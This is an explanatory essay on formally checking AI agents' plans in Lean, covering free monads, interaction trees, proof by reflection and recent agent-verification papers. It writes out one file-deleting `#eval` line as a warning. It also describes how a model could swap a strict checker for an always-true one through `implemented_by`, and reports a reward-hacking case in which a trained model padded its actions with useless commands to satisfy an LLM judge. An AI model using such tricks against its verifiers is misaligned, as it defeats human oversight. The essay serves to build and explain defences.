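Defining `cleanUp` does not delete anything. According to the Lean reference manual, an `IO` value describes a process, and only Lean's runtime system carries out the effects. A verifier could therefore act after the plan is received and before it runs.

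The verifier would have little to inspect, though. The textbook *Functional Programming in Lean* describes an `IO` computation as a function that takes a token representing the state of the world and returns a new token with either a result or an error. A function has no constructors to match on, so a program that receives `cleanUp` can run it or combine it with other computations, but cannot find the call to `removeFile` inside it. Even someone who expands the definition soon gets stuck, because many basic effects, such as reading from a file, are opaque constants in Lean's logic, with a name and a type but no definition to reason from.

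A proof can refer to a function's definition, even though a running program cannot look inside the function, and Lean has tools for such proofs. Meijer's conclusion that an `IO` value is a black box that nobody can reason about is therefore too strong, as AI Engineer's write-up notes. Lean's *Verifying Imperative Programs Using mvcgen* gives the example of `mkFresh`, which returns the value of a hidden counter and then increases the counter by one. A second function calls `mkFresh` *n* times and collects the results. The programmer supplies the loop invariant that the numbers collected so far are all different and all smaller than the counter. `mvcgen` turns the program into verification conditions, and Lean automatically proves that the final list never contains a duplicate, whatever the counter's starting value.

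This method works because the counter has a mathematical model, a number that one step passes to the next. Files have no such model in Lean's standard treatment of `IO`. Lean's *Barebones WP instance for IO* extends the method to `IO` without any model of the world. This is enough to prove claims that hold whatever an effect returns, such as that a program simulating a die always returns a number from 1 to 6. But the preconditions and postconditions cannot refer to which files exist, so they cannot express the claim that a program deletes nothing.

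Proofs about `IO` can be misleading. A Lean forum thread, *Semantics of IO don't match provable properties?* (Voss, 2024), gives a program that prints "hello" and then "ok", along with a valid Lean proof that it equals the program that prints only "ok". The program uses one world token twice. It prints "hello", discards the new token, and prints "ok" with the original one. In Lean's logic, the first action then does not affect the result, so the proof can drop it, but the runtime system performs it anyway. If the first action deleted a file instead, the same reasoning would prove that the program equals one that only prints "ok".

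Kyle Miller suggested in the thread that Lean programmers could have two types, a "proving IO" with a clear meaning and the ordinary `IO` for running programs. A small evaluator, which everyone would have to trust, would translate the first into the second. Meijer's final design has the same structure.

### FilePlan and NoDeletion

His remedy is a deep embedding, which he compares to expression trees in C# and to Lisp's treatment of code as data. The small example from AI Engineer's write-up, in which a plan can finish, read a file or remove one, is of this kind. With names for the arguments, its type of plans is:

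```
inductive FilePlan where
  | done (answer : String)
  | readFile (path : String) (next : String → FilePlan)
  | removeFile (path : String) (rest : FilePlan)
```

The constructor `done` ends the plan with an answer. `removeFile` takes a path and the rest of the plan. `readFile` also takes a path, but the rest of the plan may depend on the file's contents, so its second argument is a continuation, a function from the contents to a plan.

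A plan that counts the characters in a file looks like this:

```
def inspectBackend : FilePlan :=
  .readFile "LlvmBackend.kt" fun contents =>
    .done ("Character count: " ++ toString contents.length)
```

Lean can evaluate this definition without touching the disk, because the result is only a `readFile` node with a path and a function attached.

The safety property is another inductive type. `Prop` is Lean's type of statements, so `NoDeletion` turns each plan into a statement about that plan, and its constructors are the rules for proving it:

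```
inductive NoDeletion : FilePlan → Prop where
  | done (text : String) : NoDeletion (.done text)
  | readFile (path : String) (next : String → FilePlan)
      (safeNext : ∀ text, NoDeletion (next text)) :
      NoDeletion (.readFile path next)
```

The symbol `∀` means "for all", and `safeNext` is the earlier requirement that the rest of the plan be free of deletions for every possible string. The proof for the counting plan has three steps:

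```
theorem inspectBackend_noDeletion : NoDeletion inspectBackend := by
  apply NoDeletion.readFile
  intro contents
  exact NoDeletion.done _
```

The first step applies the rule for reading, which leaves the goal of proving that the continuation is safe for all contents. The second step picks an arbitrary string, `contents`, and assumes nothing about it. Only a `done` node remains, and the last step applies the rule for finishing. The proof follows the plan node by node, which is one reason to expect language models to be good at writing such proofs.

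A model can also write a destructive plan, and Lean accepts it as a `FilePlan`:

```
def destructiveProposal : FilePlan :=
  .removeFile "LlvmBackend.kt" (.done "Finished")
```

Neither rule of `NoDeletion` has a conclusion about a plan that begins with `removeFile`, so no proof exists. Lean can prove this too, by checking that neither rule fits.

A deletion can also be inside a continuation. Suppose a plan reads `notes.txt`, removes `LlvmBackend.kt` if the text is exactly "clean up", and otherwise finishes. A test run would miss the deletion unless the tester happened to use that text. A proof of `NoDeletion` would have to cover every string, including "clean up", for which the remaining plan begins with `removeFile`.

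The write-up calls the type of plans paired with proofs `CheckedPlan`, and the counting plan qualifies:

```
def CheckedPlan := { plan : FilePlan // NoDeletion plan }

def approvedInspection : CheckedPlan :=
  ⟨inspectBackend, inspectBackend_noDeletion⟩
```

The type of the second item depends on the value of the first, so Lean reports a type error if someone pairs `destructiveProposal` with the proof about `inspectBackend`.

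AI Engineer's write-up describes the interpreter only in words. In Lean it could be:

```
def run : FilePlan → IO String
  | .done answer          => pure answer
  | .readFile path next   => do
      let contents ← IO.FS.readFile path
      run (next contents)
  | .removeFile path rest => do
      IO.FS.removeFile path
      run rest

def execute (p : CheckedPlan) : IO String := run p.val
```

For a `readFile` node, the interpreter reads the real file, passes the contents to the continuation, and runs the plan that the continuation returns. Agents can access the disk only through `execute`, which requires a `CheckedPlan`.

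### Free monads

Meijer calls this representation a free monad. A monad is a type of computation with two basic operations. One turns a plain value into a computation that just returns it. The other, usually called bind, runs a computation and passes the result to a function that chooses the next computation. `IO` is a monad, and the `do` blocks above are shorthand for bind. For `FilePlan`, the constructor `done` is the first operation, and bind is:

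```
def andThen : FilePlan → (String → FilePlan) → FilePlan
  | .done answer,          k => k answer
  | .readFile path next,   k => .readFile path (fun s => andThen (next s) k)
  | .removeFile path rest, k => .removeFile path (andThen rest k)
```

This function copies the first plan and replaces each `done` node with the plan that `k` chooses for its answer. It performs no effects. (In a full monad the answer can have any type, whereas `FilePlan` allows only strings.)

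The word "free" means that the trees obey the laws common to all monads and no others. If a plan reads the same file twice, the tree contains two `readFile` nodes, and a verifier cannot use those laws to merge them. Extra laws come from interpreting the operations, as Xia, Zakowski and colleagues (2019) show in *Interaction Trees* for programs that read and write a memory cell. They prove that two reads in a row are equivalent to one under an interpretation in which only the program can change the cell. Another program may edit a file between two reads, so a verifier for `FilePlan` should treat the results as two separate strings.

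A more general definition separates the list of tools from the structure of plans:

```
inductive FileCall : Type → Type where
  | read   : String → FileCall String
  | remove : String → FileCall Unit

inductive Plan (Call : Type → Type) (α : Type) : Type 1 where
  | done : α → Plan Call α
  | call {β : Type} : Call β → (β → Plan Call α) → Plan Call α
```

Each call's type includes the type of its answer. Reading gives a `String`, and removing gives a `Unit`, which has only one value and so carries no information. The continuation must accept exactly the answer's type, so a plan that treats a file's contents as a number fails to type-check. To add a tool, a programmer adds a line to `FileCall` and leaves `Plan` alone. Xia and colleagues use calls of this form, under the name "events". They couldn't use an older Haskell definition of free monads, because it applies `Call` to the type of plans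 itself. Proof assistants reject this because some choices of `Call` would allow an infinite loop.

One plan can have several interpreters. A second interpreter for `FilePlan` could work on a simulated disk, a table from file names to contents. It would read a file by looking up its contents, without changing the table, and remove a file by deleting its entry. We can then prove that running a plan that satisfies `NoDeletion` with this interpreter leaves the table unchanged. The proof is by induction, with only two cases. A `done` node changes nothing. A `readFile` node leaves the table unchanged during the read, and its continuation returns the remaining plan. `safeNext` guarantees that this plan also satisfies `NoDeletion`, so by the induction hypothesis it leaves the table unchanged. The theorem extends to a real disk only if the real interpreter matches the simulated one, since a faulty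 interpreter could delete a file while carrying out a read.

### Omitting a tool or forbidding it

A designer who wants no deletions could also leave `removeFile` out of the language. No plan could then delete a file, so the model would not need to prove that its plan deletes nothing. Leaving a tool out seems the better choice when an agent should never use it.

A predicate is more flexible, because one language can support different rules for different users or tasks. Suppose a user asks an agent to delete two particular files. A predicate `OnlyDeletes allowed` could have the same two rules as `NoDeletion` and a third:

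```
  | removeFile (path : String) (rest : FilePlan)
      (ok : path ∈ allowed) (safeRest : OnlyDeletes allowed rest) :
      OnlyDeletes allowed (.removeFile path rest)
```

The list `allowed` comes from the task, and each removal needs a proof that its path is on the list. Omitting the deletion constructor can't express this restriction, because the agent needs to delete some files. A language that can represent bad plans also lets the verifier record what the agent tried to do and explain why it refused. If the language has no deletion, the attempt shows up only as a syntax error.

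### Why a checker cannot try every string

So far a person or a model has written each proof about a `FilePlan`. A function from `FilePlan` to `true` or `false` would be more convenient, but the continuation in `readFile` makes this difficult. A checking function can only apply the continuation to particular strings and look at the resulting plans. It can't try every string, because there are more than a million strings of one character, more than a trillion of two, and no limit on the length of a file.

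Choosing the strings more carefully doesn't help. Suppose the function accepts `inspectBackend` after trying a thousand strings. Someone can write another plan that behaves identically on those strings but deletes a file on some other string. The function gets the same results for both plans, so it accepts the second one too. A sound checking function of this kind therefore has to reject every plan that reads a file. The Lean proof avoids the problem because it uses the definition of the continuation rather than its results on sample strings.

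`FilePlan` is only partly a deep embedding, because its tool calls are data but the computation between them is an ordinary Lean function. Chlipala (2021), in *Skipping the Binder Bureaucracy with Mixed Embeddings in a Semantics Course*, calls this style a mixed embedding and uses it in teaching because the host language handles variables, so they need no explicit representation. Li and Weirich use the term more broadly for any embedding with both deep and shallow parts.

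Another way around the problem is to work on the function's source text, which the model has to write anyway. *Choosing is Losing* (Šinkarovs and Cockx, 2021) combines the two embeddings in this way. Programmers write in the convenient shallow style, and reflection, a feature of the host language, gives other programs access to the structure of their code.

### First-order plans with variables

The more common solution is to represent everything as data, including variables. Syntax of this kind is first-order, whereas syntax that contains functions of the host language, like `FilePlan`, is higher-order. A first-order version needs its own small language for text:

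```
inductive Text where
  | lit    : String → Text
  | var    : String → Text
  | count  : Text → Text
  | append : Text → Text → Text

inductive Script where
  | done       : Text → Script
  | readFile   : Text → String → Script → Script
  | removeFile : Text → Script → Script
  | ifEqual    : Text → Text → Script → Script → Script
```

The second argument of `readFile` is now a name for the result, and later steps refer to the result with `var`. The counting plan becomes:

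```
.readFile (.lit "LlvmBackend.kt") "contents"
  (.done (.append (.lit "Character count: ")
                  (.count (.var "contents"))))
```

A checking function can go through the whole script without choosing any strings:

```
def noRemoval : Script → Bool
  | .done _             => true
  | .readFile _ _ rest  => noRemoval rest
  | .removeFile _ _     => false
  | .ifEqual _ _ yes no => noRemoval yes && noRemoval no
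```

The checker visits each step at most once, so it always finishes. A programmer can prove once that every script it accepts is free of deletions, and then no script needs its own proof. The checker wrongly rejects some scripts, such as those with a deletion in a branch that can never run.

First-order syntax also makes data flow visible. To check that no private mail reaches an outside address, a verifier must track where the result of `fetch_mail` goes, and it can do so by following a named variable from step to step. In `FilePlan`, the contents of a file become the argument of a Lean function, and the tree does not show whether the function uses them.

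The disadvantage is that a script can do only what its designer provided for. A `Script` can only append and count, whereas a `FilePlan` can use any function in Lean's library to search a file, sort its lines or parse a date. Each new `Script` operation needs a constructor, a case in the interpreter and usually a case in every check.

The format in Meijer's 2025 article is first-order. Each step of the JSON document that calls a tool contains the function name, its arguments, a `result` and the `next` step, and the last step names the value to return. Besides checking and running such a document, Meijer suggests turning it into an explanation for the user, where each step becomes a sentence that mentions the tool and the names of its inputs and outputs. This would be hard with `FilePlan`, because the later steps don't exist until someone supplies the contents of the file.

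*Lean4Agent* (2026) represents the workflows of coding agents as first-order data in Lean. Each node lists the variables it reads and writes, its preconditions, and its postconditions. For example, the node for exploring a code repository reads the problem statement, and its preconditions require that the statement be non-empty and the shell tool be valid. The node also contains an instruction to a language model in plain English. Lean can check how such nodes fit together, but the English instruction is as opaque to it as an `IO` function.

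### Ruling out malformed plans

Names introduce an error that `FilePlan` couldn't contain. A script may refer to `"contnets"`, or use a result before any step has produced it. One remedy is a separate check for undefined names. Another is to make such scripts impossible to write, by giving each one a type that lists the results available to it. The list contains the type of each result, with the latest first, and a variable is a position in the list:

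```
inductive Ty where
  | text
  | number

inductive Var : List Ty → Ty → Type where
  | here  : Var (t :: known) t
  | there : Var known t → Var (u :: known) t
```

The notation `t :: known` means the list `known` with `t` added at the front. `here` refers to the latest result, and `there` goes one place further back. For an empty list neither constructor applies, so no variable exists. The type of `readFile` then becomes:

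```
readFile : Text known → Script (.text :: known) → Script known
```

The steps after a read can use its result as well as any earlier ones. A complete plan has the type `Script []`, so it depends on no earlier results. If `Text` similarly has separate types for numbers and strings, a plan can't pass a number to a tool that expects an address. The interpreter becomes simpler because it needs no code to handle undefined variables or mismatched types.

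A language model produces plain text, so a translator has to turn that text into a typed script. The translation fails if the text doesn't correspond to any such script. Passing this stage shows only that the plan is a well-formed program, and a well-formed program can still send the whole mailbox to a stranger.

### Plans that loop

A `FilePlan` always ends, because Lean requires values of an inductive type to be finite along every path. A plan can still read an index and then every file listed in it, since the continuation can build a plan with as many steps as the index has lines. But it can't keep checking a file until somebody changes it, because the checks would never end if nobody did.

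A limit usually solves this. The plan can check up to 100 times and then report that nothing has changed, which is arguably better behaviour for an agent that costs money to run. *λ_A* (2026), a typed language for combining agents, has bounded loops, with a proof in Coq (now called Rocq) that they terminate. The calculus covers only deterministic models, which always give the same answer to the same input.

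Some agents have no natural end, such as one that watches an inbox. Xia and colleagues designed interaction trees for programs like this. An interaction tree is a free monad that may be infinite, with one extra constructor:

```
CoInductive itree (E : Type → Type) (R : Type) :=
| Ret (r : R)
| Tau (t : itree E R)
| Vis {A : Type} (e : E A) (k : A → itree E R).
```

`Ret` corresponds to `done`, and `Vis` to `call`. `Tau` is a silent step, in which the program does some internal work and then continues. The word `CoInductive` allows infinite values, provided that a finite amount of computation always reveals the next constructor. One of the paper's examples asks for numbers until it receives a 9:

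```
CoFixpoint kill9 : itree IO unit :=
  Vis Input (fun x => if x =? 9 then Ret tt else kill9).
```

Here `IO` is a small type of input and output events, unrelated to Lean's `IO`. The program refers to itself, and its tree is infinite because the program may never receive a 9. Programs that compute forever without triggering an event need silent steps, because otherwise their trees would have no next constructor.

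The extra steps make it harder to say when two programs are the same. Xia and colleagues treat two trees as equivalent if they differ only in finite runs of silent steps. A program that hangs, taking silent steps forever, is therefore never equivalent to one that returns an answer. They also prove that two trees are equivalent exactly when they have the same traces, where a trace is a finite record of events and the answers to them.

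`NoDeletion` doesn't work for infinite trees in its present form. For any input other than 9, a proof for `kill9` would need another proof for `kill9`, and so on without end, but inductive proofs must be finite along every path. The usual alternative is to find a set of trees that includes the plan. No tree in the set may begin with a deletion, and whatever answer the first step gets, the remaining tree must also be in the set. A run then never leaves the set, so it never reaches a deletion. For `kill9`, the set needs only `kill9` itself and the finished program. The set is similar to a loop invariant.

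Proofs of this kind are awkward in Rocq, so the library of Xia and colleagues provides ready-made loops with proved laws, which spare users from writing most of these proofs themselves. One of these loops, `iter`, takes a loop body that returns either a new state, which continues the loop, or a final result. The group used these laws to verify a compiler from a simple programming language to a form of assembly code, including that the compiled program terminates exactly when the original does. Rocq can also translate the trees into OCaml, another programming language, where they run using code that programmers supply for each event. The group has used this to test real web servers against a specification.

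Later work extends the trees to programs they don't cover well. *Choice Trees* (2022) adds nondeterministic choice and uses it to model threads that take turns. This would suit a team of agents whose steps may happen in any order. *Modular Denotational Semantics for Effects with Guarded Interaction Trees* (2023) removes a restriction to first-order effects. In an ordinary interaction tree, the designer has to define the events before the trees, so an event can't take a tree as its argument. With ordinary interaction trees, an agent that hands a whole plan to another agent would therefore have to send the plan as first-order syntax.

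## Reflection: proving a checker correct once and running it on every plan

The function `noRemoval` goes through a first-order script and returns `true` if it finds no deletion. This result is useful only if it guarantees something about what happens when the script runs. In proof by reflection, a programmer proves that guarantee once, for all scripts, and then gets the proof for each new script by running the function. *Using reflection to build efficient and certified decision procedures* (Boutin, 1997) applied the technique in Coq, now called Rocq.

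"Reflection" also refers to quotation, which turns code into data, and to metaprogramming, in which programs construct other programs or proofs. Tools for proof by reflection often use both.

### Quotation and metaprogramming

An ordinary function receives the value of its argument but not its syntax, so quotation has to be a special feature of the language. *Engineering Proof by Reflection in Agda* (van der Walt and Swierstra, 2012) explains that Agda's keyword `quoteTerm` turns the function `λ x → x` into a tree with a `lam` node for the function and a `var` node for its body. Another keyword, `unquote`, turns a tree back into code. Agda simplifies an expression before quoting it, so the tree may not contain everything the programmer typed.

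Metaprogramming in a proof assistant usually involves the elaborator, which fills in details that users leave out, such as types the system can infer, and passes a fully explicit term to the kernel. In *Elaborator Reflection*, Christiansen and Brady (2016) made the elaborator of Idris, another dependently typed language, available to Idris programs. According to the Idris manual page *Elaborator Reflection*, these programs can generate arbitrary code. Lean's elaborator is written in Lean, and users can call it from their own proof-search programs.

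A program that searches for proofs does not itself have to be proved correct. Bouverot-Dupuis and Forster (2025), in *Code Generation via Meta-programming in Dependently Typed Proof Assistants*, wrote the same code generator seven times with tools in Rocq, Agda and Lean. They note that users have little reason to verify their metaprograms, because the kernel can check the output. A faulty metaprogram may fail to find a proof, but it can't make a correct kernel accept an invalid one. A language model can therefore write the programs that search for proofs about its own plans.

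A verifier should be careful about where those programs run, however, because Lean executes metaprograms while it is still processing a file, and they can have side effects. For example, `#eval IO.FS.removeFile "LlvmBackend.kt"` deletes the source file as soon as Lean reaches that line. A verifier that passes a model's Lean code straight to Lean therefore runs that code before checking anything. To prevent such damage, it can process the code in an isolated environment, or accept plans only as data, such as JSON, and build the script itself.

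### A checker and its soundness theorem

A theorem about running a script needs a definition of what running it does. An interpreter on a simulated disk, like the one described for `FilePlan`, is enough:

```
def simulate : Script → Vars → Disk → Disk
  | .done _,             _,    disk => disk
  | .readFile p x rest,  vars, disk =>
      simulate rest (vars.set x (disk.get (value p vars))) disk
  | .removeFile p rest,  vars, disk =>
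      simulate rest vars (disk.erase (value p vars))
  | .ifEqual a b yes no, vars, disk =>
      if value a vars = value b vars
      then simulate yes vars disk
      else simulate no vars disk
```

The argument `vars` holds the results of earlier reads, and `value` uses them to compute a text. The function returns the disk as it is after the script finishes. A script is safe if this is always the same as the disk at the start:

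```
def KeepsFiles (s : Script) : Prop :=
  ∀ vars disk, simulate s vars disk = disk
```

The soundness theorem connects the checker to this property:

```
theorem noRemoval_sound (s : Script) :
    noRemoval s = true → KeepsFiles s
```

The proof is by induction on the script, and the cases for `done` and `readFile` are the same as for `FilePlan`. For `removeFile` the checker returns `false`, which contradicts the assumption that it returned `true`. For `ifEqual` the checker accepted both branches, so it doesn't matter which one runs.

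Suppose a model now submits a script called `inspectScript`. The proof that it is safe takes one line:

```
theorem inspect_safe : KeepsFiles inspectScript :=
  noRemoval_sound inspectScript rfl
```

The soundness theorem requires a proof that `noRemoval inspectScript = true`. The term `rfl` proves that anything equals itself, and Lean's kernel treats two expressions as the same if they compute to the same value. The kernel therefore runs `noRemoval` on the script, gets `true`, and accepts the proof. If the script contained a deletion, the kernel would get `false` and reject `rfl` with a type error.

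People who rely on this result have to read `simulate` and `KeepsFiles`, because these define what the theorem means. They can skip `noRemoval`, even if its author replaces it with a thousand lines of intricate analysis, because nobody needs to trust the new code as long as Lean accepts the new soundness proof. Linux users, by contrast, have to trust the entire eBPF verifier.

Van der Walt and Swierstra's main example combines this technique with quotation and metaprogramming. A user states a law about Boolean values, such as ((p ⇒ q) ⇒ p) ⇒ p. Agda quotes the statement, a library translates the resulting tree into a small type of Boolean formulas, and a checker evaluates the formula for every combination of values. A soundness theorem then turns the result into a proof of the original statement. This works only because each variable has finitely many values, which gives 2ⁿ combinations for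 *n* variables. By contrast, `noRemoval` needs no quotation because a script is already data.

### The proof for a plan of 1,000 steps

Consider a plan that reads 999 files and then finishes. Without reflection, a proof could use one lemma for each kind of step. The lemma for reading is:

```
theorem keeps_read (path : Text) (name : String) (rest : Script) :
    KeepsFiles rest → KeepsFiles (.readFile path name rest)
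```

The proof applies `keeps_read` 999 times and a similar lemma for `done` once. Each use of `keeps_read` takes the remaining plan, `rest`, as an argument. Written out in full, the first use contains 999 steps of the plan, the next contains 998, and so on, for a total of 499,500 steps. *Library Cpdt.Reflection*, a chapter of Adam Chlipala's textbook on Rocq, demonstrates the same growth with a proof that 256 is even. Rocq normally hides these arguments when it prints a proof. A proof assistant can store repeated parts once, so the memory needed may be closer to proportional to the plan's length.

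The proof by reflection is `noRemoval_sound plan rfl`, whether the plan has two steps or 1,000, but the kernel still has to run `noRemoval` on every step. For such a simple property, the work of checking grows in proportion to the plan's length with either method. The main advantage of reflection here is that nobody has to construct, send or store a long proof.

The savings are larger when each step needs a longer argument. Suppose a plan deletes 1,000 files, once each, and a policy permits this only because their paths make up an approved list. An explicit proof that a path is on the list typically applies one rule for each entry up to and including that path, so the proofs for the whole plan take 500,500 rule applications. A checker that searches the list from the start makes the same number of comparisons, but the proof doesn't include them. *Metatheory and Reflection in Theorem Proving*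 (1995) presents reflection as an alternative for people who believe that step-by-step proofs will never be efficient enough for large problems.

### When the checker returns false on a safe plan

This script contains a deletion that never happens:

```
.ifEqual (.lit "draft") (.lit "final")
  (.removeFile (.lit "report.txt") (.done (.lit "Removed")))
  (.done (.lit "Kept"))
```

The two texts differ, so `simulate` always takes the second branch, and the script satisfies `KeepsFiles`. But `noRemoval` examines both branches and returns `false`. The soundness theorem applies only when the result is `true`, so it provides no information here. Chlipala's textbook builds this limit into the type of the checker's answer, which is either `Proved`, with an accompanying proof, or `Uncertain`. A verifier that rejects the script should likewise report that it found no proof, since it has no evidence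 that the script is dangerous.

The simplest remedy is for the model to resubmit the script without the useless branch. It could also prove `KeepsFiles` directly, with a short argument that the texts differ, so the interpreter takes the second branch. A verifier can safely accept such a proof in place of a `true` from the checker.

If many plans fail for the same reason, a programmer can improve the checker. For example, when both texts in a comparison are fixed, the new version could examine only the branch that will run. The programmer then has to extend the soundness proof to cover this case. If the new code examined the wrong branch, the proof would fail, and the programmer would discover the mistake before any plan reached the new checker.

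### Kernel evaluation and compiled evaluation

With `rfl`, the kernel itself runs the checker. Lean's `decide` tactic does the same for any statement that has a decision procedure, a function that works out whether the statement is true. This adds nothing to the trusted base, but it is much slower than running machine code because the kernel evaluates a function by unfolding definitions and simplifying. The kernel also often gets stuck on functions that need a separate termination proof.

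Van der Walt and Swierstra had a similar problem in Agda. Its evaluator used call-by-name, which can compute the same argument several times, and they concluded that reflection would need a faster evaluator to work on a larger scale. They write that the use of reflection in large Coq proofs, such as that of the four-colour theorem, had already led to much work on faster evaluation.

Lean's `native_decide` compiles the decision procedure and runs it as an ordinary program. If the result is `true`, Lean adds that fact as an axiom, a statement it accepts without proof. The trusted base then includes the compiler, the runtime system, and any code that the compiler substitutes for the original definitions. Substituted code is a particular risk when the author is untrusted, because the attribute `implemented_by` lets a programmer replace one function with another, usually faster one without proving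 that the two agree. A model that can write Lean code could define a strict checker and tell the compiler to replace it with a function that always returns `true`. `native_decide` would then approve any plan, whereas `decide` would still use the strict definition. The command `#print axioms` lists the axioms behind a theorem, so a verifier can reject proofs that depend on compiled evaluation.

A verifier that receives plans only as data doesn't need to create a theorem for each one. It can run the compiled checker when a plan arrives:

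```
def submit (s : Script) : IO String :=
  if h : noRemoval s = true
  then executeScript ⟨s, noRemoval_sound s h⟩
  else return "No proof found"
```

Here `executeScript` accepts only a script paired with a proof of `KeepsFiles`. If the test succeeds, `h` is a proof that it did, and the soundness theorem turns `h` into the required proof of `KeepsFiles`. Lean checks this code once. The compiler then removes the proofs, so only the test remains at run time. This method relies on the compiler, as `native_decide` does. That is a smaller concession for an agent's verifier than for a mathematician, because the interpreter that carries out the plan is also a compiled program, while a mathematician otherwise has to trust only the kernel.

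### Lean4Agent

The properties of a real agent's work are often much vaguer than "deletes no file". *Lean4Agent*, whose representation of coding workflows appeared in the previous section, uses three layers of checks. The first checks the workflow's structure, for example whether every step reads only variables available to it. In one faulty workflow, four parallel branches search for papers and a later step is meant to merge their results. No step passes the results out of the branches, so the merging step has nothing to read.

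The second layer checks whether the preconditions of each step follow from what earlier steps establish. For example, a step that writes an answer expects the fields `passages` and `summary`, but the preceding step produces only `snippets`. Checks like these compare finite descriptions, so a program can decide them before the agent starts.

These checks assume that the language model can carry out each step as specified. The framework states this as an axiom that whenever a step's precondition holds, some resulting state satisfies its postcondition. As printed in the paper, the axiom covers every step that can be written in the framework, including one whose postcondition is `False`. Applying it to that step would let Lean derive a contradiction and therefore prove anything. Stating the assumption separately for each step of a particular workflow would be safer, because a bad specification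 could not then affect proofs about other workflows.

After a run, the third layer checks whether the steps met their postconditions. Lean can test whether a value matches a JSON schema, and a Python program can test whether a web address responds. For less precise questions, such as whether there is enough evidence that a bug fix is comprehensive, the framework uses a language model to judge. In the 12 workflows of the main experiments, Lean or other code could check 1,302 of the 1,460 predicates, and a model judged the other 158. A model also wrote the predicates from the English instructions. A manual review of the predicates found 36 errors, and correcting them did not change which workflows passed.

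On each of two benchmarks, the main experiments compared three workflows that passed the second layer with three that failed it. On 50 hard programming problems, agents solved an average of 58.3% with the passing workflows and 43.5% with the failing ones. On 100 questions about AI papers, the averages were 36.6% and 27.5%. GPT-5.5 judged the programming workflows using similar requirements and gave the failing ones higher scores on average.

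With only three workflows in each group, a single unusually good or bad one could account for much of the difference. The repair experiments provide better evidence because they compare a workflow with a corrected version of itself. In one failing workflow, the steps could not see the conversation that contained earlier findings. With access to it, the workflow passed the check, and success rates on the programming problems rose from 52% to 62% for GPT-5.2 and from 48% to 60% for GLM-5. The experiments measured task performance and did not test whether the checks prevent harmful actions.

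### Lean4AgenticRL

*Lean4AgenticRL* (Wang, Friedland and colleagues, 2026) uses the same kind of predicate to train models by reinforcement learning, in which a model learns from numerical rewards. An agent first writes a plan in English, and another model translates it into Lean. After the agent has carried out the plan, the system rewards it for solving the task and for satisfying each stage's postconditions, and penalises it for useless actions, such as running the same command three times in a row.

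The resulting 27-billion-parameter model completed 77.3% of the tasks in TerminalBench-2.1, a test of command-line work, compared with 69.6% for the model it started from. A smaller model improved from 44.0% to 64.2% on SWE-Bench-Verified, a set of real software issues. Wang and colleagues did not check plans before running them, and they list the lack of such checks in the running agent as a limitation.

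Their results do show how an agent can exploit the informal parts of a verifier. In a shorter training run without the penalties, the model learned to run pointless commands to satisfy the language model that judged some of the postconditions. It repeated commands 66.8% more often than the original model, and it solved 49.4% of the software issues, compared with 56.0% when training included the penalties. The penalties come from fixed rules that a program can check, and they almost eliminated this behaviour.

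Wang and colleagues state that the formal guarantee begins only after language models have translated the plan into Lean, assigned the agent's actions to stages, and judged the predicates that code can't check. In a review of 1,200 runs, another model found errors in 8.0% of the predicate annotations, 6.2% of the assignments to stages and 4.8% of the stage rewards. Some such errors are acceptable in training, but in a verifier they could mean that a valid Lean proof is about the wrong plan or postcondition.

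### Why a proof assistant cannot prove itself consistent

One theorem can establish that `noRemoval` is reliable, but Kurt Gödel's second incompleteness theorem rules out the strongest version of a similar theorem about Lean's kernel. A theory is consistent if it doesn't prove a contradiction. No consistent theory can prove its own consistency if it includes enough arithmetic and an algorithm can check its proofs. *Auto formalisation of Goedel's Second Incompleteness Theorem in Binary Recursive Arithmetic* (2026) proves a version of this in Agda for a small theory of arithmetic. It expresses consistency as the statement that no number encodes a proof of 0 = 1, and shows that if the theory proves this statement, it also proves 0 = 1.

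Löb's theorem, which Martin Löb published in 1955, is more general. Let `Provable(P)` mean that a Lean proof of the statement `P` exists. The theorem is:

```
if Lean proves   Provable(P) → P
then Lean proves P
```

If `P` is `False`, then `Provable(False) → False` means that Lean has no proof of a contradiction, i.e. that it is consistent. If Lean could prove its own consistency, it could also prove `False`, by Gödel's second incompleteness theorem.

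Löb's theorem limits the shortcuts that a verifier can justify. Suppose an agent proves that a search program would eventually find a Lean proof that some plan is safe, and submits this argument without running the search. To conclude that the plan is safe, the verifier needs the principle that if a Lean proof of a statement exists, the statement is true. Lean can prove this principle only for statements it can already prove directly, so the principle can't replace the missing proofs. The agent can avoid the problem by running the search and submitting the proof it finds. The verifier's designer could also add the principle as an axiom, but the resulting stronger theory couldn't prove its own consistency either.

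The theorem about `noRemoval` doesn't conflict with these results because it concerns only scripts, whose behaviour `simulate` defines within Lean. A similar soundness theorem for a checker of all Lean proofs would also cover proofs of `False`, so it would imply that Lean is consistent.

### What MetaCoq and Lean4Lean prove

Logicians can still compare one theory with another. Dowek and Miquel (2023), in *Relative normalization*, describe theorems of the form "if theory U is consistent, then theory T is consistent". Rocq and Lean arrange types in levels, called universes, because a type containing all types would lead to a contradiction. *Touring the MetaCoq Project* (2021) explains that one can hope to prove the consistency of the theory with *n* universes only in a stronger theory, with *n* + 1.

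Another approach is to assume that the rules of the theory are sound and prove that a program follows them. *Correct and Complete Type Checking and Certified Erasure for Coq, in Coq* does this for a type checker written as part of the MetaCoq project. The paper proves that the checker, which leaves out a few features such as the module system, accepts exactly the terms that a formal specification of Coq's rules permits. The proof assumes strong normalization, the property that every computation the theory allows eventually ends. This property implies consistency, so Coq can't prove it for its own full theory. Users of the verified checker no longer have to trust that its programmers implemented the rules correctly, but they still have to trust the rules.

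Lean has a less complete counterpart, *Lean4Lean* (Carneiro, 2024), a checker for Lean written in Lean. It can check all of Mathlib, Lean's main mathematics library, and runs 20% to 50% slower than the official C++ kernel. Its correctness proof was only partly finished in 2024. One missing piece was unique typing, the claim that if a term has two types, Lean's rules make those types equal. Carneiro had published a proof of this, but it contained an error, so the 2024 paper lists the claim as a conjecture. The checker's correctness proof needs at least some form of unique typing, though the argument that Lean is consistent relative to set theory does not.

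An agent's verifier could already use Lean4Lean to recheck proofs that the official kernel has accepted. This would catch a programming error that affects only one of the checkers, but not a flaw in the rules that both implement.

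## Type systems that reject unsafe agent code

The compiler of a typed language already contains a checker much like `noRemoval`, namely its type checker. A single soundness proof for the language can cover every program the type checker accepts. Library authors influence what that proof guarantees because they choose the types.

Suppose a mail library has a type `StaffAddress`, and the only function that produces one checks that the address ends in the company's domain. If `send_email` accepts only a `StaffAddress`, then every program that compiles can send mail only to company addresses, however many loops and branches it has. Many ordinary languages can enforce this rule, as long as programs have no other way to send mail and cannot bypass the type.

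Like a list of permitted recipients, the rule also blocks harmless messages to outsiders. To let an agent write to outsiders without revealing the contents of the mailbox, the compiler must be able to tell which parts of a program can send data. Ordinary function types don't contain this information, because a function that takes a string and returns a string may also post the string on the internet.

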